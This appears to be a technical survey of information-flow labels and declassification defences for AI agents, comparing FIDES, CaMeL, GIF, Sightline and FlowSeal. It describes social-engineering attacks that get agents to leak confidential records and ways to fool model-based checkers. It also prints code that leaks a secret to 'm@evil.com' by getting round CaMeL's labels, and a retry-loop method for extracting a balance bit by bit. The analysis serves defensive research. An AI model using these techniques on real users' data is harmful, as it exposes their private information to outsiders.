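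Without a classifier, the system has to treat such data as public and risk a leak, treat it as restricted and block harmless work, or ask a person. Frequent approval requests tire people, and Kolluri and colleagues warn that users start to approve them without reading carefully.

The strongest argument for a classifier is that pasted text arrives without a correct label. If the system treats that text as public by default, a classifier that catches 90% of confidential pastes prevents nine out of ten leaks that FIDES would otherwise allow, even though it is less accurate than a correct label would be. The system can join the classifier's label to the default one, so that the classifier can add restrictions but never remove them. Text the classifier misses is then no less protected than before, though a refusal may itself reveal that the text was sensitive.

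The argument is weaker when the default is restrictive, because a classifier that lifts restrictions can release data that the system would have withheld. Costa and colleagues consider a similar step for integrity, where the system marks a document as trusted after a prompt injection classifier checks it. They warn that relying on such detectors could weaken the security guarantees.

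## How labels follow data through summaries and other rewritten text

Suppose Ana asks her assistant for a one-line reminder based on the merger memo, and it writes "Keep the week of 9 March free for Oslo." The reminder doesn't mention Northwind, a price or a merger, so a classifier will probably label it public. But Northwind is based in Oslo, and only people involved in the deal know that Ana is going there. A competitor who saw the reminder would learn the place and the date.

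The memo's content has lost its restrictive label because a model rewrote it, which is a form of laundering. This can happen without an attacker, because a short summary tends to drop the names, figures and technical terms that a classifier relies on.

### Three ways to label a summary

Suppose the assistant read the memo, labelled {Ana, Ben}, and the public calendar before writing the reminder. The system could join the labels of everything the assistant read, which gives {Ana, Ben}. It could have a model read the reminder and assign a new label, which would probably be "everyone". Or it could estimate which documents influenced the reminder and join only their labels. This gives {Ana, Ben} if the estimate is right and "everyone" if it misses the memo.

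The join always keeps the memo's label, but it causes the label creep that kept FIDES from completing many of its tasks. Influence estimation is meant to remove unnecessary labels and keep the others.

Reclassification also removes unnecessary labels, but the text of a reminder is not enough to identify them. Suppose the public calendar already listed a trade fair in Oslo that week. The assistant could then have written the same reminder from the calendar alone, and anyone could be allowed to see it. A classifier that reads only the reminder must give this version the same label as the one written from confidential data.

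Tools can also cause data to lose its private label without changing the text. *RTBAS* (Zhong, Chen and colleagues, 2025) describes an agent with two tools. One sends messages and may handle private data, and the other returns sent messages and labels them public. If the agent sends its own user a private message and then reads it back, the unchanged text is now labeled public. The join cannot prevent this, because it combines whatever labels the tools supply.

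### Several agents and stored memories

Reclassification becomes riskier as text passes through more hands. Let y₀ be the memo and let each later text yₖ be a rewrite of the one before. With joins, each label is at least as restrictive as the previous one, so the memo's restrictions survive any number of rewrites:

$$\text{label}(y_0) \sqsubseteq \text{label}(y_1) \sqsubseteq \dots \sqsubseteq \text{label}(y_k)$$

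With reclassification, the label of the kth version, yₖ, depends only on the words of yₖ. The classifier can correctly restrict the first five versions and then label a vaguer sixth version as public.

Suppose that on Monday a research agent reads the memo and saves the Oslo reminder to a memory that several agents share. A classifier labels the reminder public. On Thursday a scheduling agent, which has never opened the memo, retrieves the reminder and emails Dev to move some building work out of that week. The gate allows the email because everything the scheduling agent read was labeled public. Joining labels on Thursday doesn't help, because the memo's label disappeared on Monday. An auditor would find no confidential document in the scheduling agent's history. *GIF* describes the same danger in long-running agents, whose later actions may depend on secrets that are no longer in the immediate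 context.

Alternatively, the system can store the label with the memory. *SPA* (Girrens and Wang, 2026) describes an agent that plans each request from the user's words and short descriptions of stored results, without seeing the results. When the plan needs a stored result, the system retrieves it with its original label. Thursday's email would then carry the label {Ana, Ben}, and the gate would stop it.

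Girrens and Wang tested this on a version of AgentDojo in which later requests build on earlier ones. Turning on the label checks lowered task completion from 62.5% to 35.3%. Most of the loss came from integrity checks, so the result is little evidence of how much confidentiality labels alone would lower completion. With the checks on, the agent retrieved an available stored result in 89.9% of the cases that called for it, compared with 95.4% without them.

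### What survives rewriting

Reclassifying rewritten text as public is correct if the rewrite removed the secret, but in measurements so far, rewriting has not reliably done so. Secrets got through Langiu's summarising router, and parts of identifying phrases often survived the redaction and rephrasing that Agyemang and colleagues tested. Both tests checked for the original wording, so neither would count a clue that a model had reworded.

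Other researchers test whether a text's meaning survives redaction. *RedacBench* (2026) extracts the individual statements in a text and uses them to test redaction by masking words and by an adversarial method. *Contrastive Privacy* (2026) tests 15 sanitisers based on language models on 49 Reddit comments about the Avengers films. The sanitisers had to hide which film series the comments were about, so deleting the word "Avengers" was not enough if a comment still described the plot.

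*Contrastive Privacy* uses a language model to recognise related ideas, and notes that its measure could fail for obscure plot details that the model doesn't connect to the films. The Oslo reminder would cause the same problem, because a model that doesn't know where Northwind is based wouldn't connect the reminder to the company, but a competitor would.

*LLMs as Linguistic Chameleons* (2026) cites earlier research in which language models could both anonymise text and identify the people in anonymised text. Whether a rewrite is safe therefore depends on what its readers know and which models they have, and both can change after the text has left the system. A label inherited from the memo doesn't depend on guessing what a reader could work out.

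### Writing the answer again from fewer sources

A system that estimates how much each document influenced a text can keep the text and drop the labels of documents that seem not to have mattered, or it can remove those documents and have the model write the text again. A wrong estimate has very different consequences in the two cases.

Siddiqui, Gaonkar and colleagues (2024), in *Permissive Information-Flow Analysis for Large Language Models*, chose to write the text again. The model first writes an answer y using all the available documents, C. The system then considers a less restrictive label L′ and keeps only C′, the documents whose labels are no more restrictive than L′. To check whether C′ is sufficient, it measures the perplexity of the original answer, which is 1 divided by the average probability (strictly, the geometric mean) that the model gives each token. It accepts L′ if removing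 the other documents raises perplexity by no more than a tolerance λ:

$$\mathrm{PPL}(y \mid C') - \mathrm{PPL}(y \mid C) \le \lambda$$

The system searches for the least restrictive labels that pass this test and picks one. It then runs the model again on the reduced set of documents and returns only the new answer, with the label L′.

In one experiment, the tolerance λ was 0.2. Suppose the tokens in Ana's weekly summary have an average probability of 80% when the model sees the memo, which gives a perplexity of 1.25. If the average drops to 70% without the memo, perplexity rises to 1.43. This is within the tolerance, so the system leaves out the memo and its label. If the average drops to 50%, perplexity rises to 2 and the system keeps the label.

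Averaging over tokens can hide a secret. Suppose the summary has 200 tokens and only the word "Oslo" depends on the memo. Without the memo, "Oslo" becomes 800 times less likely and nothing else changes. Perplexity rises only to

$$1.25 \times 800^{1/200} \approx 1.29$$

so the system wrongly concludes that the memo didn't matter. If it kept the original summary, it would send "Oslo" out with a public label. But it writes the summary again without the memo, so the new version can contain "Oslo" only if another document mentions it or the model guesses it. Ana gets an incomplete summary, but the memo's text doesn't leak.

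The design provides this protection even if an attacker has fooled the model. The paper's formal proposition is that the search always stops, and that it finds every minimal label that passes the test, provided that adding documents never makes an answer harder to predict. Siddiqui and colleagues note that real models don't always meet this condition.

The benchmarks therefore measure how useful the method is. In a test with news articles, which had trust labels instead of confidentiality labels, a less restrictive label was possible for 647 of 3,465 questions. A 7-billion-parameter Llama 2 model found it for 57% of these. About 23% of the labels it relaxed were too permissive, because the system left out a source that the answer had needed. In another test, each question came with 14 documents, each with a different label. The method found exactly the right sets of documents for 86% of questions.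 Asking the model which documents had influenced the answer worked for only 2% to 13%, depending on the model's size.

The search can be slow because the number of model runs can grow exponentially with the number of documents when every document has a different set of readers. RTBAS replaces the search with a screener that decides, before each step, which parts of the conversation the model needs. The system joins the labels of those parts and masks everything the joined label doesn't cover. The model writes its message or chooses a tool only after this masking. If the screener misses the memo and selects only public parts, the system masks the memo and the model writes to Dev without seeing it.

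Zhong and colleagues built two screeners. One is a language model that reads the conversation, with each part marked, and lists the relevant parts. The other uses attention, the mechanism by which a transformer draws on earlier tokens when it processes a later one. This screener measures how much the attention to each part affects the output, and a small neural network uses these measurements to decide whether the part is relevant. The network was right 81% of the time on test data.

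The researchers wrote 37 privacy tasks involving payments, flights and shopping, in which the agent should ask for confirmation before it uses private data. The error counts below follow their discussion, which contradicts their definitions of the two error rates. The language model screener asked unnecessarily in three tasks and masked private data that the task needed in four. The attention screener asked unnecessarily in six tasks and masked needed data in four. Asking before every tool call would have been unnecessary in 11 tasks. The masking mistakes made the agent less useful but did not release private data.

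Zhong and colleagues conclude that screener mistakes cannot compromise security. This is true of the text, but the choice of label still depends on the secret. The gate blocks the email to Dev if the memo matters and lets it through otherwise. Dev can therefore learn something from whether the email arrives, so neither design achieves noninterference.

### Scoring how strongly each part of the input counts

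GIF measures influence without writing the text again. A language model represents each token as a list of numbers called an embedding. GIF considers adding a small amount of random noise, U, to the embeddings of one stretch of the input, such as the memo. It then asks how much the next token, Y, would reveal about that noise. The exact answer is the mutual information I(U; Y), which is too expensive to compute, so GIF uses the score

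$$\mathrm{GIF}(\tau) = \tfrac{1}{2}\log\det(I + \tau M)$$

Here τ is the variance of the noise, I on the right is the identity matrix, and M measures how much a small change in each direction shifts the next token's probabilities. If small changes to the memo barely affect those probabilities, the score is close to zero.

The main theorem, which the researchers checked in Lean, states that

$$I(U; Y) \le \mathrm{GIF}(\tau) + o(\tau) \quad \text{as } \tau \to 0$$

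The term o(τ) is an error that shrinks faster than τ. "Locally sound" means that, for vanishingly small changes to one stretch of one fixed prompt, the score does not understate the effect on the next token. The theorem doesn't cover replacing the memo with a different memo, which is the comparison that noninterference requires.

Xu, Li and colleagues (2026), in *Sightline*, prove that this gap can hide an entire secret. Their example fits the message to Dev about whether the lobby will be busy. Let u be 1 if the deal is on and −1 if it is off, and suppose the model writes "busy" with probability

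$$p = \frac{1}{1 + e^{-20u}}$$

and "quiet" otherwise. When the deal is on, "busy" is almost certain, and a tiny change in u has almost no effect. The slope of log p is about 0.00000004, and GIF's score is also close to zero. When the deal is off, "quiet" is just as certain. The message tells Dev whether the deal is on, but the score suggests that almost nothing has flowed.

Models are often this confident. Xu and colleagues found that for one in five outputs of Qwen3-8B, alternative tokens had less than 1% of the probability on average.

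In one example in *GIF*, an agent turns private notes about a neighbour into a public comment and leaves out the home address. The address gets a score of zero, but this doesn't prove that the agent would have written the same comment if the address had been different, although the paper describes the score as certifying that no information flowed from it.

The system ranks parts of the input by their scores and passes the highest-ranked parts to a language model, which decides whether to allow the action. If GIF ranks the relevant part of the memo too low, the model doesn't receive it and may approve an email that reveals the secret from the memo.

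The benchmark results are weaker for confidentiality than for integrity. In one confidentiality test, the researchers supplied the correct labels for the private tokens and checked whether more of these tokens ranked highly in runs that leaked private data. When they used the top 50 tokens, a leaking run scored higher than a harmless one about 75% of the time, compared with 50% for guessing. On two prompt injection benchmarks, which test integrity, the figures were 91% and 92%.

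GIF needs access to a model's internals, which companies that sell models rarely provide. The researchers found that a small open model could analyse the outputs of much larger ones with almost no loss of accuracy in detecting prompt injections. But the theorem then applies only to the small model and not to the larger model that wrote the email.

### Learning which inputs the output uses

Sightline takes the inputs to one model call, such as a question and two documents, and predicts which of them the output used. It runs the model once over the recorded input and output and measures the attention from the output to each input. A simple classifier turns these measurements into a score for each input. The system keeps the labels of inputs that score above a threshold and drops the rest.

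Xu and colleagues proved in Lean that if no later token attends to an input, small changes to that input cannot affect the output. But every input receives some attention, and they also proved that an input can affect the output even when it receives very little. In one example, an input receives about two billionths of the attention, yet changing its value reverses the output. They compare this to an implicit flow through a branch that a program did not take.

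Dropping a particular label can't be proved safe, so a conformal method sets the threshold and keeps the average chance of missing a true dependence at or below α. Like the conformal bounds for classifiers, this guarantee assumes exchangeable data and doesn't cover inputs written by an attacker.

The bound also depends on what counts as a true dependence. Three language models read each input and output and decided by majority vote whether the output visibly reflected the input. They saw only one run at a time, so they could miss a case where a different memo would have led the assistant to leave something out.

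Xu and colleagues compared several methods on prompts from open-source programs, after calibrating each to miss about 1% of true dependences. They wrote their own versions of the other methods and tested RTBAS's attention screener without its masking. The table shows the share of unnecessary labels that each method removed for four models.

| Method | Qwen3-8B | Granite 4.2 3B | Gemma 4 E2B | Nemotron 3 Nano 4B |
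|---|---|---|---|---|
| Sightline | 65.6% | 58.5% | 61.6% | 43.9% |
| RTBAS attention screener | 29.4% | 19.3% | 14.7% | 26.8% |
| Removing one input at a time | 14.1% | 18.9% | 18.3% | 13.2% |
| GIF, extended to 32 output tokens | 0.6% | 0.9% | 1.3% | 12.1% |

GIF does badly because many true dependences occur in confident outputs, where its scores are close to zero. A threshold low enough to catch them keeps almost every label.

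Removing one input at a time fails when two documents contain the same fact. If Ben has repeated the Oslo dates in an email, the assistant can write the reminder from either the memo or the email alone. Each document then seems unnecessary, so the reminder loses both labels. Siddiqui and colleagues avoid this problem by removing all documents above the candidate label together.

Sightline is clearly the best of these methods, but its 1% miss rate is riskier than it sounds because only 12% to 14% of the inputs in these prompts had no effect on the output. If 130 of 1,000 labels are unnecessary, Sightline would remove 57 to 85 of them, along with about nine of the 870 that are needed. That is roughly one dangerous removal for every seven to ten useful ones. The miss rate is also for a single call, so the risk can add up if the assistant rewrites the reminder many times.

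On AgentDojo, with α at 5%, Sightline removed 50.0% of label creep and had a miss rate of 3.9%. The researchers also applied an integrity policy that blocks consequential tool calls that are based on untrusted data. It blocked all 34 calls that would have carried out an attack. Even if these calls were independent, the result would be compatible with a true failure rate of up to 8%.

The attack test is also weak evidence about confidentiality. The policy blocks a call if any untrusted label remains on it, so Sightline can miss some labels and still block the attack. But confidentiality may depend on a single label. If the memo is the only document Dev may not read and Sightline misses its label, the gate will let the reminder go to him.

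Sightline could be combined with Siddiqui and colleagues' approach. Sightline would pick out the documents that seemed not to matter, and the model would write the reminder again without them. This would take another model run, but if Sightline missed a dependence, the new reminder would usually be less useful rather than send Dev something from the memo.

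## Models that decide whether a message may be released

Even with accurate labels, a gate blocks some messages that should go out. For example, once Ana's assistant has read the merger memo, it can't email Dev to say that the projector in Room 2 is broken. Ana could approve the email herself, or a model could read it and approve it for her. The model would then act as a declassifier, because its approval overrides the label.

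### Guards between classified networks

Armed forces faced this problem long before AI agents existed. Many classified networks treat every file as if it were as secret as the most secret item on the network, an extreme form of label creep. A guard is a gateway that can pass files to a less secret network after comparing each file's label with a release policy. *Information sharing across security domains*, a report from the Norwegian Defence Research Establishment (FFI), compared guards with one-way links, manual review and filters. It found that guards using labels were the most general way to move information automatically in both directions.

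A guard relies on the security labels attached to files. A University of Oslo (2017) summary of Kyrre Wahl Kongsgård's doctoral thesis describes systems in which users label each file by hand, which works only if the users are honest and never make mistakes. Kongsgård, Nordbotten and colleagues (2017) point out in *Data Leakage Prevention for Secure Cross-Domain Information Exchange* that engineers can build a trustworthy guard but find it much harder to be equally sure of the labels. Guards therefore also search files for a list of "dirty words", terms that suggest secret content, but this search misses any term that nobody thought to list.

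The Norwegian researchers tried machine learning instead. Hammer, Kongsgård and colleagues (2015), in *Automatic Security Classification by Machine Learning for Cross-Domain Information Exchange*, concluded that a classifier could become useful for helping people choose labels. Kongsgård, Nordbotten and colleagues (2016), in *Data loss prevention based on text classification in controlled environments*, addressed documents that people had summarised, rewritten or assembled from pasted paragraphs. They recorded which documents had entered a closed working environment and used them to judge each new document written there, which improved detection of wrongly labelled documents. The 2017 paper tested the approach on real classified and unclassified documents, and warned that naive versions were vulnerable to manipulation.

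By then the classifier had become a second check on labels people had assigned. The University of Oslo summary claims only that the classifier makes leaks less likely.

### Agents that judge their own messages

FlowSeal, a defence for AI agents from September 2026, also compares outgoing text with its sources. *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* presents it as an alternative to defences that ask the agent itself to recognise an improper disclosure. One of those defences instructs the agent to check who sent each request for information, ask the data's owner for consent and wait for a direct reply.

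The agent decides what counts as a request for information. The researchers found three ways to stop it from recognising such a request, none of which requires prompt injection.

- **Collaborative framing.** An outsider presents the disclosure as shared work, such as filling in a section of a joint document. The agent treats this as a routine task and never starts the procedure.
- **Disclosure by omission.** The outsider supplies a list of true and invented statements and asks the agent to remove the errors. The agent writes nothing confidential, but the entries it leaves in place are the true ones. This works only if the outsider already has some good guesses.
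- **Split channels.** The request arrives through one channel, such as email, and the disclosure happens in another, such as a shared page. The agent doesn't connect the two.

The researchers ran each attack three times on each of 105 invented scenarios. The first four rows of the table show the share of sensitive items that leaked, and the last row shows how many harmless tasks the agent completed.

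| | Simple consent prompt | Strict procedure | Model that filters output | FlowSeal |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Collaborative framing | 31.8% | 52.2% | 62.2% | 0.5% |
| Disclosure by omission | 54.7% | 75.6% | 54.2% | 2.3% |
| Split channels | 13.3% | 43.8% | 63.9% | 2.2% |
| Earlier attack using false pretexts | 3.6% | 3.0% | 18.6% | 0.3% |
| Harmless tasks completed | 75.9% | 44.7% | 25.1% | 72.4% |

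The strict procedure did slightly better than the simple prompt against the earlier attack but much worse against the three new ones, where it leaked between 43.8% and 75.6% of items. FlowSeal leaked between 0% and 3.3% across all eight attacks. It completed slightly fewer harmless tasks than the simple prompt but many more than the strict procedure.

### How FlowSeal divides the work

FlowSeal takes its labels from provenance. It registers each sensitive record with its owner, its text and the people who may receive it, using sources such as email sender fields and document permissions. Code outside the agent intercepts every tool call and tracks which records the agent has read. If the agent summarises two records, the summary needs permission for both.

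The same code handles outgoing messages. It lets messages to trusted recipients through and blocks those to blacklisted ones. If the recipient is unknown, it calls an isolated model, the checker, which receives only the protected records and the proposed message. The checker returns SAFE or BLOCKED without an explanation, since an explanation could reveal protected information. Its instructions allow SAFE only if the message contains nothing that a reader could derive from a protected record. It should return BLOCKED even if the message only paraphrases, summarizes, confirms or denies something in a record.

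Access to the records gives the checker an advantage over a filter that reads only the message. For example, the reminder "Keep the week of 9 March free for Oslo" contains no obviously confidential words, so a text-only classifier would probably label it public. FlowSeal's checker could match the city and week to those in the memo. But it would probably also block the reminder if the assistant had written it from a public calendar entry about a trade fair, because the same facts appear in the memo.

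The checker also needs the full text of the records, so it must run on a machine that is allowed to hold them. If it runs in another company's cloud, every check sends the secrets to a sink.

The paper contrasts FlowSeal with FIDES but incorrectly states that FIDES leaves all enforcement to the language model. According to the FIDES paper, the system's gate compares labels in ordinary code, so an agent that mistook a disclosure for routine work would still face the label check. But once the memo was in the agent's context, FIDES would also block the email about the projector. FlowSeal uses a model to let such harmless messages through.

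### A theorem with an exception

FlowSeal gives protected records the highest label, ⊤, and outside destinations the lowest, ⊥. Writing ℓ for "the label of", the code lets the agent write content c to destination d only if

$$\ell(c) \sqsubseteq \ell(d) \quad\text{or}\quad \mathrm{declassify}(c,d) = \text{SAFE}$$

where "declassify" is the checker. The theorem states that the agent can never write content derived from a protected record to an outside destination, unless the checker wrongly answers SAFE. The proof is short. Every write passes through the intercepting code, and anything the agent writes after reading a protected record has a label above ⊥. The first condition therefore fails, and only the checker can let the message out.

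This proves that the agent can't skip the check, which is valuable because all three attacks work by preventing the agent from starting one. But it doesn't limit how often the checker is wrong. Even a checker that always answered SAFE would satisfy the theorem, because every leak would fall under the exception for wrong SAFE answers. The paper's conclusion omits this exception and describes FlowSeal as formally guaranteeing that sensitive records cannot reach unauthorised destinations.

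The theorem also covers only registered records. In one failed test, the agent revealed a health detail that was missing from the register, so the checker had nothing to compare it with.

Even a checker that made no mistakes about content would not provide noninterference, because it examines only one run and could approve the message to Dev about a busy lobby.

### How much depends on the checker

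The researchers removed or changed one part of FlowSeal at a time and repeated the collaborative framing attack.

| Version | Items leaked | Harmless tasks completed |
|---|---|---|
| Complete FlowSeal | 0.5% | 72.4% |
| Agent without FlowSeal's instructions | 8.8% | 74.4% |
| No intercepting code | 28.4% | 81.2% |
| Checker always answers SAFE | 24.9% | 79.4% |
| Checker always answers BLOCKED | 1.3% | 0% |

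All the recipients in this benchmark were unknown, so the labels never settled a case without the checker. The low leak rate and the useful work both depended on the checker's answers. When it always answered SAFE, FlowSeal leaked almost as much as it did with no intercepting code, and when it always answered BLOCKED, the agent completed no tasks.

The second row conflicts with the paper's claim that FlowSeal's instructions to the agent are "not security-critical" because the code checks every message anyway. The instructions explain how to find protected records and ask for consent. Without them, leakage rose from 0.5% to 8.8%. The code still called the checker, but the checker approved more messages that it should have blocked. The leak rate therefore depends on what the agent submits as well as on the checker.

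A version that blocks every message to an unknown recipient should leak nothing, so the 1.3% in the last row is odd. Either some text got around the gate or the model that counted the leaks made mistakes. Replacing that model with each of two others changed the complete system's score from 0.5% to 1.0% and 0.8%, so differences of this size between versions mean little.

Repeated attempts are another weakness. After a block, the agent rewords its message and tries again until the checker accepts a version or the agent gives up, and the checker may miss a leak each time. In one recorded run, the agent asked the checker about a vague rewrite in advance and received SAFE, but the checker then blocked the agent's attempt to post it. In another, the checker blocked a message containing a man's psychiatric diagnoses but accepted "currently supporting client through standard wellness protocols",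 which arguably still confirms that he is receiving help. The researchers say the checker fails mainly on paraphrases. They also suggest that an attacker could split one fact across several messages that each look harmless.

FlowSeal still performed much better than the other defences. The model that filtered output without tracing its sources leaked more than half the items in all three new attacks and completed only a quarter of the harmless tasks. That model differs from FlowSeal in other ways too, but the gap is good evidence that showing a checker the source records helps.

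The leak rates, however, apply only to the particular attacks tested. Two older attacks caused no leaks in 315 runs each. That result is compatible with a true leak rate of up to about 1% if the runs were independent, or nearly 3% if the three runs of each scenario always turned out alike. The three new attacks also target the agent's judgement, so they are weaker evidence of how the checker would hold up against someone who had studied it.

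FlowSeal also withholds data that it should release. The harmless tasks in the tables required no confidential information, but a separate test used legitimate requests for data whose owner would consent if asked. With FlowSeal, the agent disclosed only 32.7% of the items, compared with 61.0% to 85.6% under the other defences, partly because it asked for consent less often.

### Robust declassification

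An outsider's influence over what a system releases was a subject of security research long before language models. Zdancewic and Myers (2001), in *Robust Declassification*, introduced a condition for it. Attackers must not be able to affect what information a system releases, or whether it releases any. Here is a program that fails:

```
if shared_page.says_owner_agreed:
    send("dev", memo.signing_date)
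```

Anybody who can edit the shared page can obtain the signing date. To state the condition exactly, let V(s, a) be everything an attacker sees when the secret is s and the attacker takes action a. Leaving aside programs that never finish, declassification is robust when

$$V(s,a) = V(s',a) \;\Rightarrow\; V(s,a') = V(s',a') \quad \text{for all } s, s', a, a'$$

If a program is robust, an attacker who can't distinguish two secrets with one action can't distinguish them with any other, so an attacker who interferes learns no more than one who only watches. A robust program can still release information inappropriately. For example, a program that emailed a confidential memo to everyone each Monday would be robust, because no attacker could change what it sent.

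*Enforcing Robust Declassification and Qualified Robustness* (Myers, Sabelfeld and Zdancewic) shows how a compiler can enforce robust declassification. The compiler rejects a program if an attacker could influence either the declassified value or the decision to declassify it. A model that reads an attacker's text before approving a release fails this test, and experiments suggest that this is a problem in practice.

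*Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* reports a small test on live Gmail and Notion accounts with PrivacyChecker, another defence that uses a model as a judge. In one case, the attacker's page described disclosing a man's diagnoses to his ex-wife as coordinating medical treatment. PrivacyChecker adopted that description and approved the disclosure. Its verdicts were only advisory, so the agent could have disclosed the diagnoses even if PrivacyChecker had rejected the request. In the omission attack, 34.7% of the items leaked under PrivacyChecker and none under FlowSeal, though this test counted only word-for-word disclosures.

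FlowSeal's checker doesn't read the attacker's messages or pages, so an attacker can't address it directly. But it reads the agent's draft, which the agent may have written in response to that material. By the compiler's standard, the draft is under the attacker's influence, so FlowSeal also fails the test. If the checker never approved protected content, the attacker could exploit only the pattern of approvals and blocks. But the checker's error rate is unproved, and both FlowSeal's resistance to influence and its theorem depend on it.

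The omission attack resembles an older problem that Myers and colleagues describe. If an attacker can make a login page treat some other secret as the password, they can test guesses about that secret by trying to log in. An outsider can likewise test guesses about a user's records by giving the user's agent a list of claims to correct.

Strict robustness rules out some reasonable behaviour. If Dev asks for the signing date and Ana is happy for him to have it, his question should affect what the assistant releases. Myers and colleagues give the example of a shop that sells information and lets each buyer choose an item. To allow this, the programmer marks the buyer's choice as acceptable with an `endorse` command like LLMbda's. The resulting weaker condition, qualified robustness, treats an endorsed value as if it could be anything, so the programmer should endorse a choice only if every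 option is acceptable. The attacker must not control whether the endorsement happens. *The LLMbda Calculus* proposes a similar rule for agents but doesn't yet define exactly what property the rule should guarantee.

Endorsement works well for a short list of options. Ana can let Dev choose between the signing date and the room number because she is willing to release either. She can't reasonably endorse a free-text request, because Dev could ask for anything in the memo. *Context-to-Execution Integrity for LLM Agents* (2026) applies a similar restriction to the model. The model may propose a release, but only trusted code can issue it, and only in a narrow form such as a time interval.

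### Showing the declassifier only what mattered

FlowSeal's checker decides whether a message contains protected information, while the owner decides whether the recipient should have it. The declassifier in *GIF* also has to consider whether the recipient should have the information, because the user's request may require sharing private data. For example, if Ana asks an agent to order flowers for her home, the florist needs her address.

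For each proposed action, the declassifier receives the one to three passages with the highest flow scores, along with a little context and the user's task. The researchers tested four language models in this role and compared each with the same model reading the agent's complete history, using two benchmarks of prompt injection and one of privacy leakage.

The shortened evidence worked about as well as the complete history or better, with detection scores 0.97 to 1.22 times as high. The smallest model, Qwen 3 8B, improved most, probably because the decisive words were no longer mixed in with thousands of irrelevant ones. With three passages, it matched GPT-5.5 on the two prompt injection benchmarks at less than one-eightieth of the cost.

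The benefit was smaller for confidentiality. With one passage, the declassifier used 27% to 37% as many tokens as the full-history judge on the prompt injection benchmarks, but 76% to 81% on the privacy benchmark. The web-browsing agent in that benchmark keeps little history, so there was less to leave out.

These ratios show that the selection preserves most of what the judge needs, but not that the judge is reliable. If a full-history judge caught 70% of leaks, a declassifier that did equally well would still miss 30%. The researchers do not formally define what such a declassifier should allow, and leave that to future work.

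The selection can also expose the declassifier to an attacker's words. When a prompt injection has steered the agent, the most influential passage is often the injection itself. Seeing it helps the declassifier recognise the attack, but also lets the attacker argue for approval. The benchmarks' injections are mainly designed to redirect the agent, so they are a weak test of whether an attacker could also persuade the declassifier.

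## Branches, refusals and routing records that reveal the secret

A gate that blocks every confidential word can still leak a secret, because people outside the system can often see whether an email arrived, which model answered a request or how long the answer took, and each of these can depend on confidential data. Ordinary programs already leak this way. A learned label adds another leak, because the model computes the label from the text that the label is supposed to protect.

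### A leak through the branch that did not run

CaMeL, the agent design in which a trusted model writes a program before anything reads the documents, blocks the simplest implicit flow. Suppose the program contains this line:

```
if account.balance > threshold: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

The message is a fixed string, but the condition is secret, so CaMeL treats everything inside the branch as secret and refuses to send the email. Garby and colleagues found a way around this that uses two extra variables:

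```
rich = True
tmp = True
if account.balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

Both variables start with public labels. The table follows them through the program.

| Line | Balance above the threshold | Balance at or below it |
|---|---|---|
| `if account.balance > threshold` | `tmp` becomes false and secret | Skipped, so `tmp` stays true and public |
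| `if tmp` | Skipped, so `rich` stays true and public | `rich` becomes false and stays public |
| `if rich` | The condition is public, so CaMeL sends the email | No email |

The email arrives exactly when the balance is above the threshold. The example adds an email to one that Fenton gave in the 1970s. CaMeL raises a variable's label only when the program assigns to that variable, so when a high balance makes the program skip `rich = False`, `rich` stays public.

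An outsider can't simply insert these five lines into CaMeL's program, and the model is unlikely to write them by accident. But the example shows that CaMeL's labels are not reliable for every program the model might write, which matters because the labels are meant to make it unnecessary to trust that program.

### One bit per run, for as many runs as it takes

When CaMeL refuses an action, the program stops with an error. An ordinary Python loop then gets a revised program from the model and runs it. The label tracking doesn't cover this loop, so each new attempt starts without restrictive labels, even though it depends on what happened in the previous one.

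Whether a program stops with an error can depend on a secret. The one-line program above does so if the balance exceeds the threshold and otherwise finishes normally. Most formal systems, including LLMbda's theorem, permit a leak of one bit per run. CaMeL's loop is a problem because it can run the program again with a different threshold.

Suppose the balance is a whole number of dollars from 0 to 1,048,575. The first run tests whether it is above 524,287, and each later run splits the remaining range in half. Since 2²⁰ = 1,048,576, the loop finds the exact balance after 20 runs, and the value it finds is not labeled secret.

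CaMeL censors error messages to limit what information passes from one attempt to the next, but Garby and colleagues note that this gives no formal guarantee. Censoring the messages also wouldn't stop a run's failure from leaking information, because the loop must detect the failure in order to try again.

Garby and colleagues' agent, Randori, retries only on simulated tools. These practice runs don't raise label errors, so a refusal can come only during the real run, and it ends that run. A program can't safely catch the error and continue, because what it did next would depend on the secret.

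Girrens and Wang's agent, SPA, gives its planner one attempt at each request, and the planner never receives refusals or tool results. SPA checks the complete plan, including its branches, before any tool runs, so a refusal can't depend on what the tools return. SPA completed 29.0% of the original AgentDojo tasks with these checks on and 53.0% without them. Integrity checks again accounted for most of the drop.

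### A label for the control context

The standard way to prevent leaks through branches is to label the control context. This label, usually called the program-counter label and written pc, is the join of the labels of all the conditions that determined whether the program would reach the current line. Inside the branch that tests the bank balance, pc is secret, so any value the program assigns there becomes secret too.

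CaMeL does this much already. What it lacks is a rule about the label that a variable had before the assignment. Garby and colleagues credit this rule to Austin and Flanagan. It allows a program to change a variable x only if

$$pc \sqsubseteq \mathrm{label}(x)$$

With this rule, the five-line program stops at the assignment on its third line when the balance is high, because `pc` is secret and `tmp` is public. When the balance is low, the program skips that assignment, sets `rich` to false and finishes. No email goes out in either case, but anyone who can see whether the program finished still learns one bit about the balance.

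LLMbda applies this rule by banning writes to a public conversation from inside a secret branch. It also uses the conversation's label as the pc for any code in the model's reply. That covers choices made inside the model, but it is a very broad form of label creep.

For ordinary code, a compiler can check both branches in advance. Zheng and Myers, in *Dynamic Security Labels and Static Information Flow Control*, give this example:

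```
if s <= 0 then x := 0 else y := 0
```

A type checker accepts the line only if information about s may flow into both x and y. A run-time monitor checks only the assignment that runs. If information about s may flow into y but not into x, the monitor reports an error only when s is zero or negative, so the absence of an error reveals that s is positive.

Checking a program in advance is harder if an error can make it jump to other code. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) lists such jumps among the features of CaMeL's restricted Python that prevent strong guarantees about information flow. It recommends a small special-purpose language with explicit conditions and limited loops. SPA's plans use such a language, with only six types of step.

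### A label that reveals the text

The starting labels in these examples contained no secrets. Anybody may know that bank balances are confidential, and the merger memo would keep its label {Ana, Ben} even if the deal collapsed. But a content label depends on what the text says. If a classifier marks a text as confidential because it describes a merger, the label reveals something about the text, and so does anything the system does because of it.

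Suppose Ana's router keeps confidential requests on a local model. A technician who can't read the requests notices that 15 of hers stayed local this week, compared with none the week before, and guesses that she is working on something confidential. A refusal can reveal the same thing, and so can a delay if the local model is slower than the cloud model. An approval can also leak information, as in the disclosure-by-omission attack, where the entries an agent left in place were the true ones.

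Improving the classifier makes this leak worse, from revealing nothing about the text when the router chooses at random to revealing exactly which requests were confidential when it never makes a mistake.

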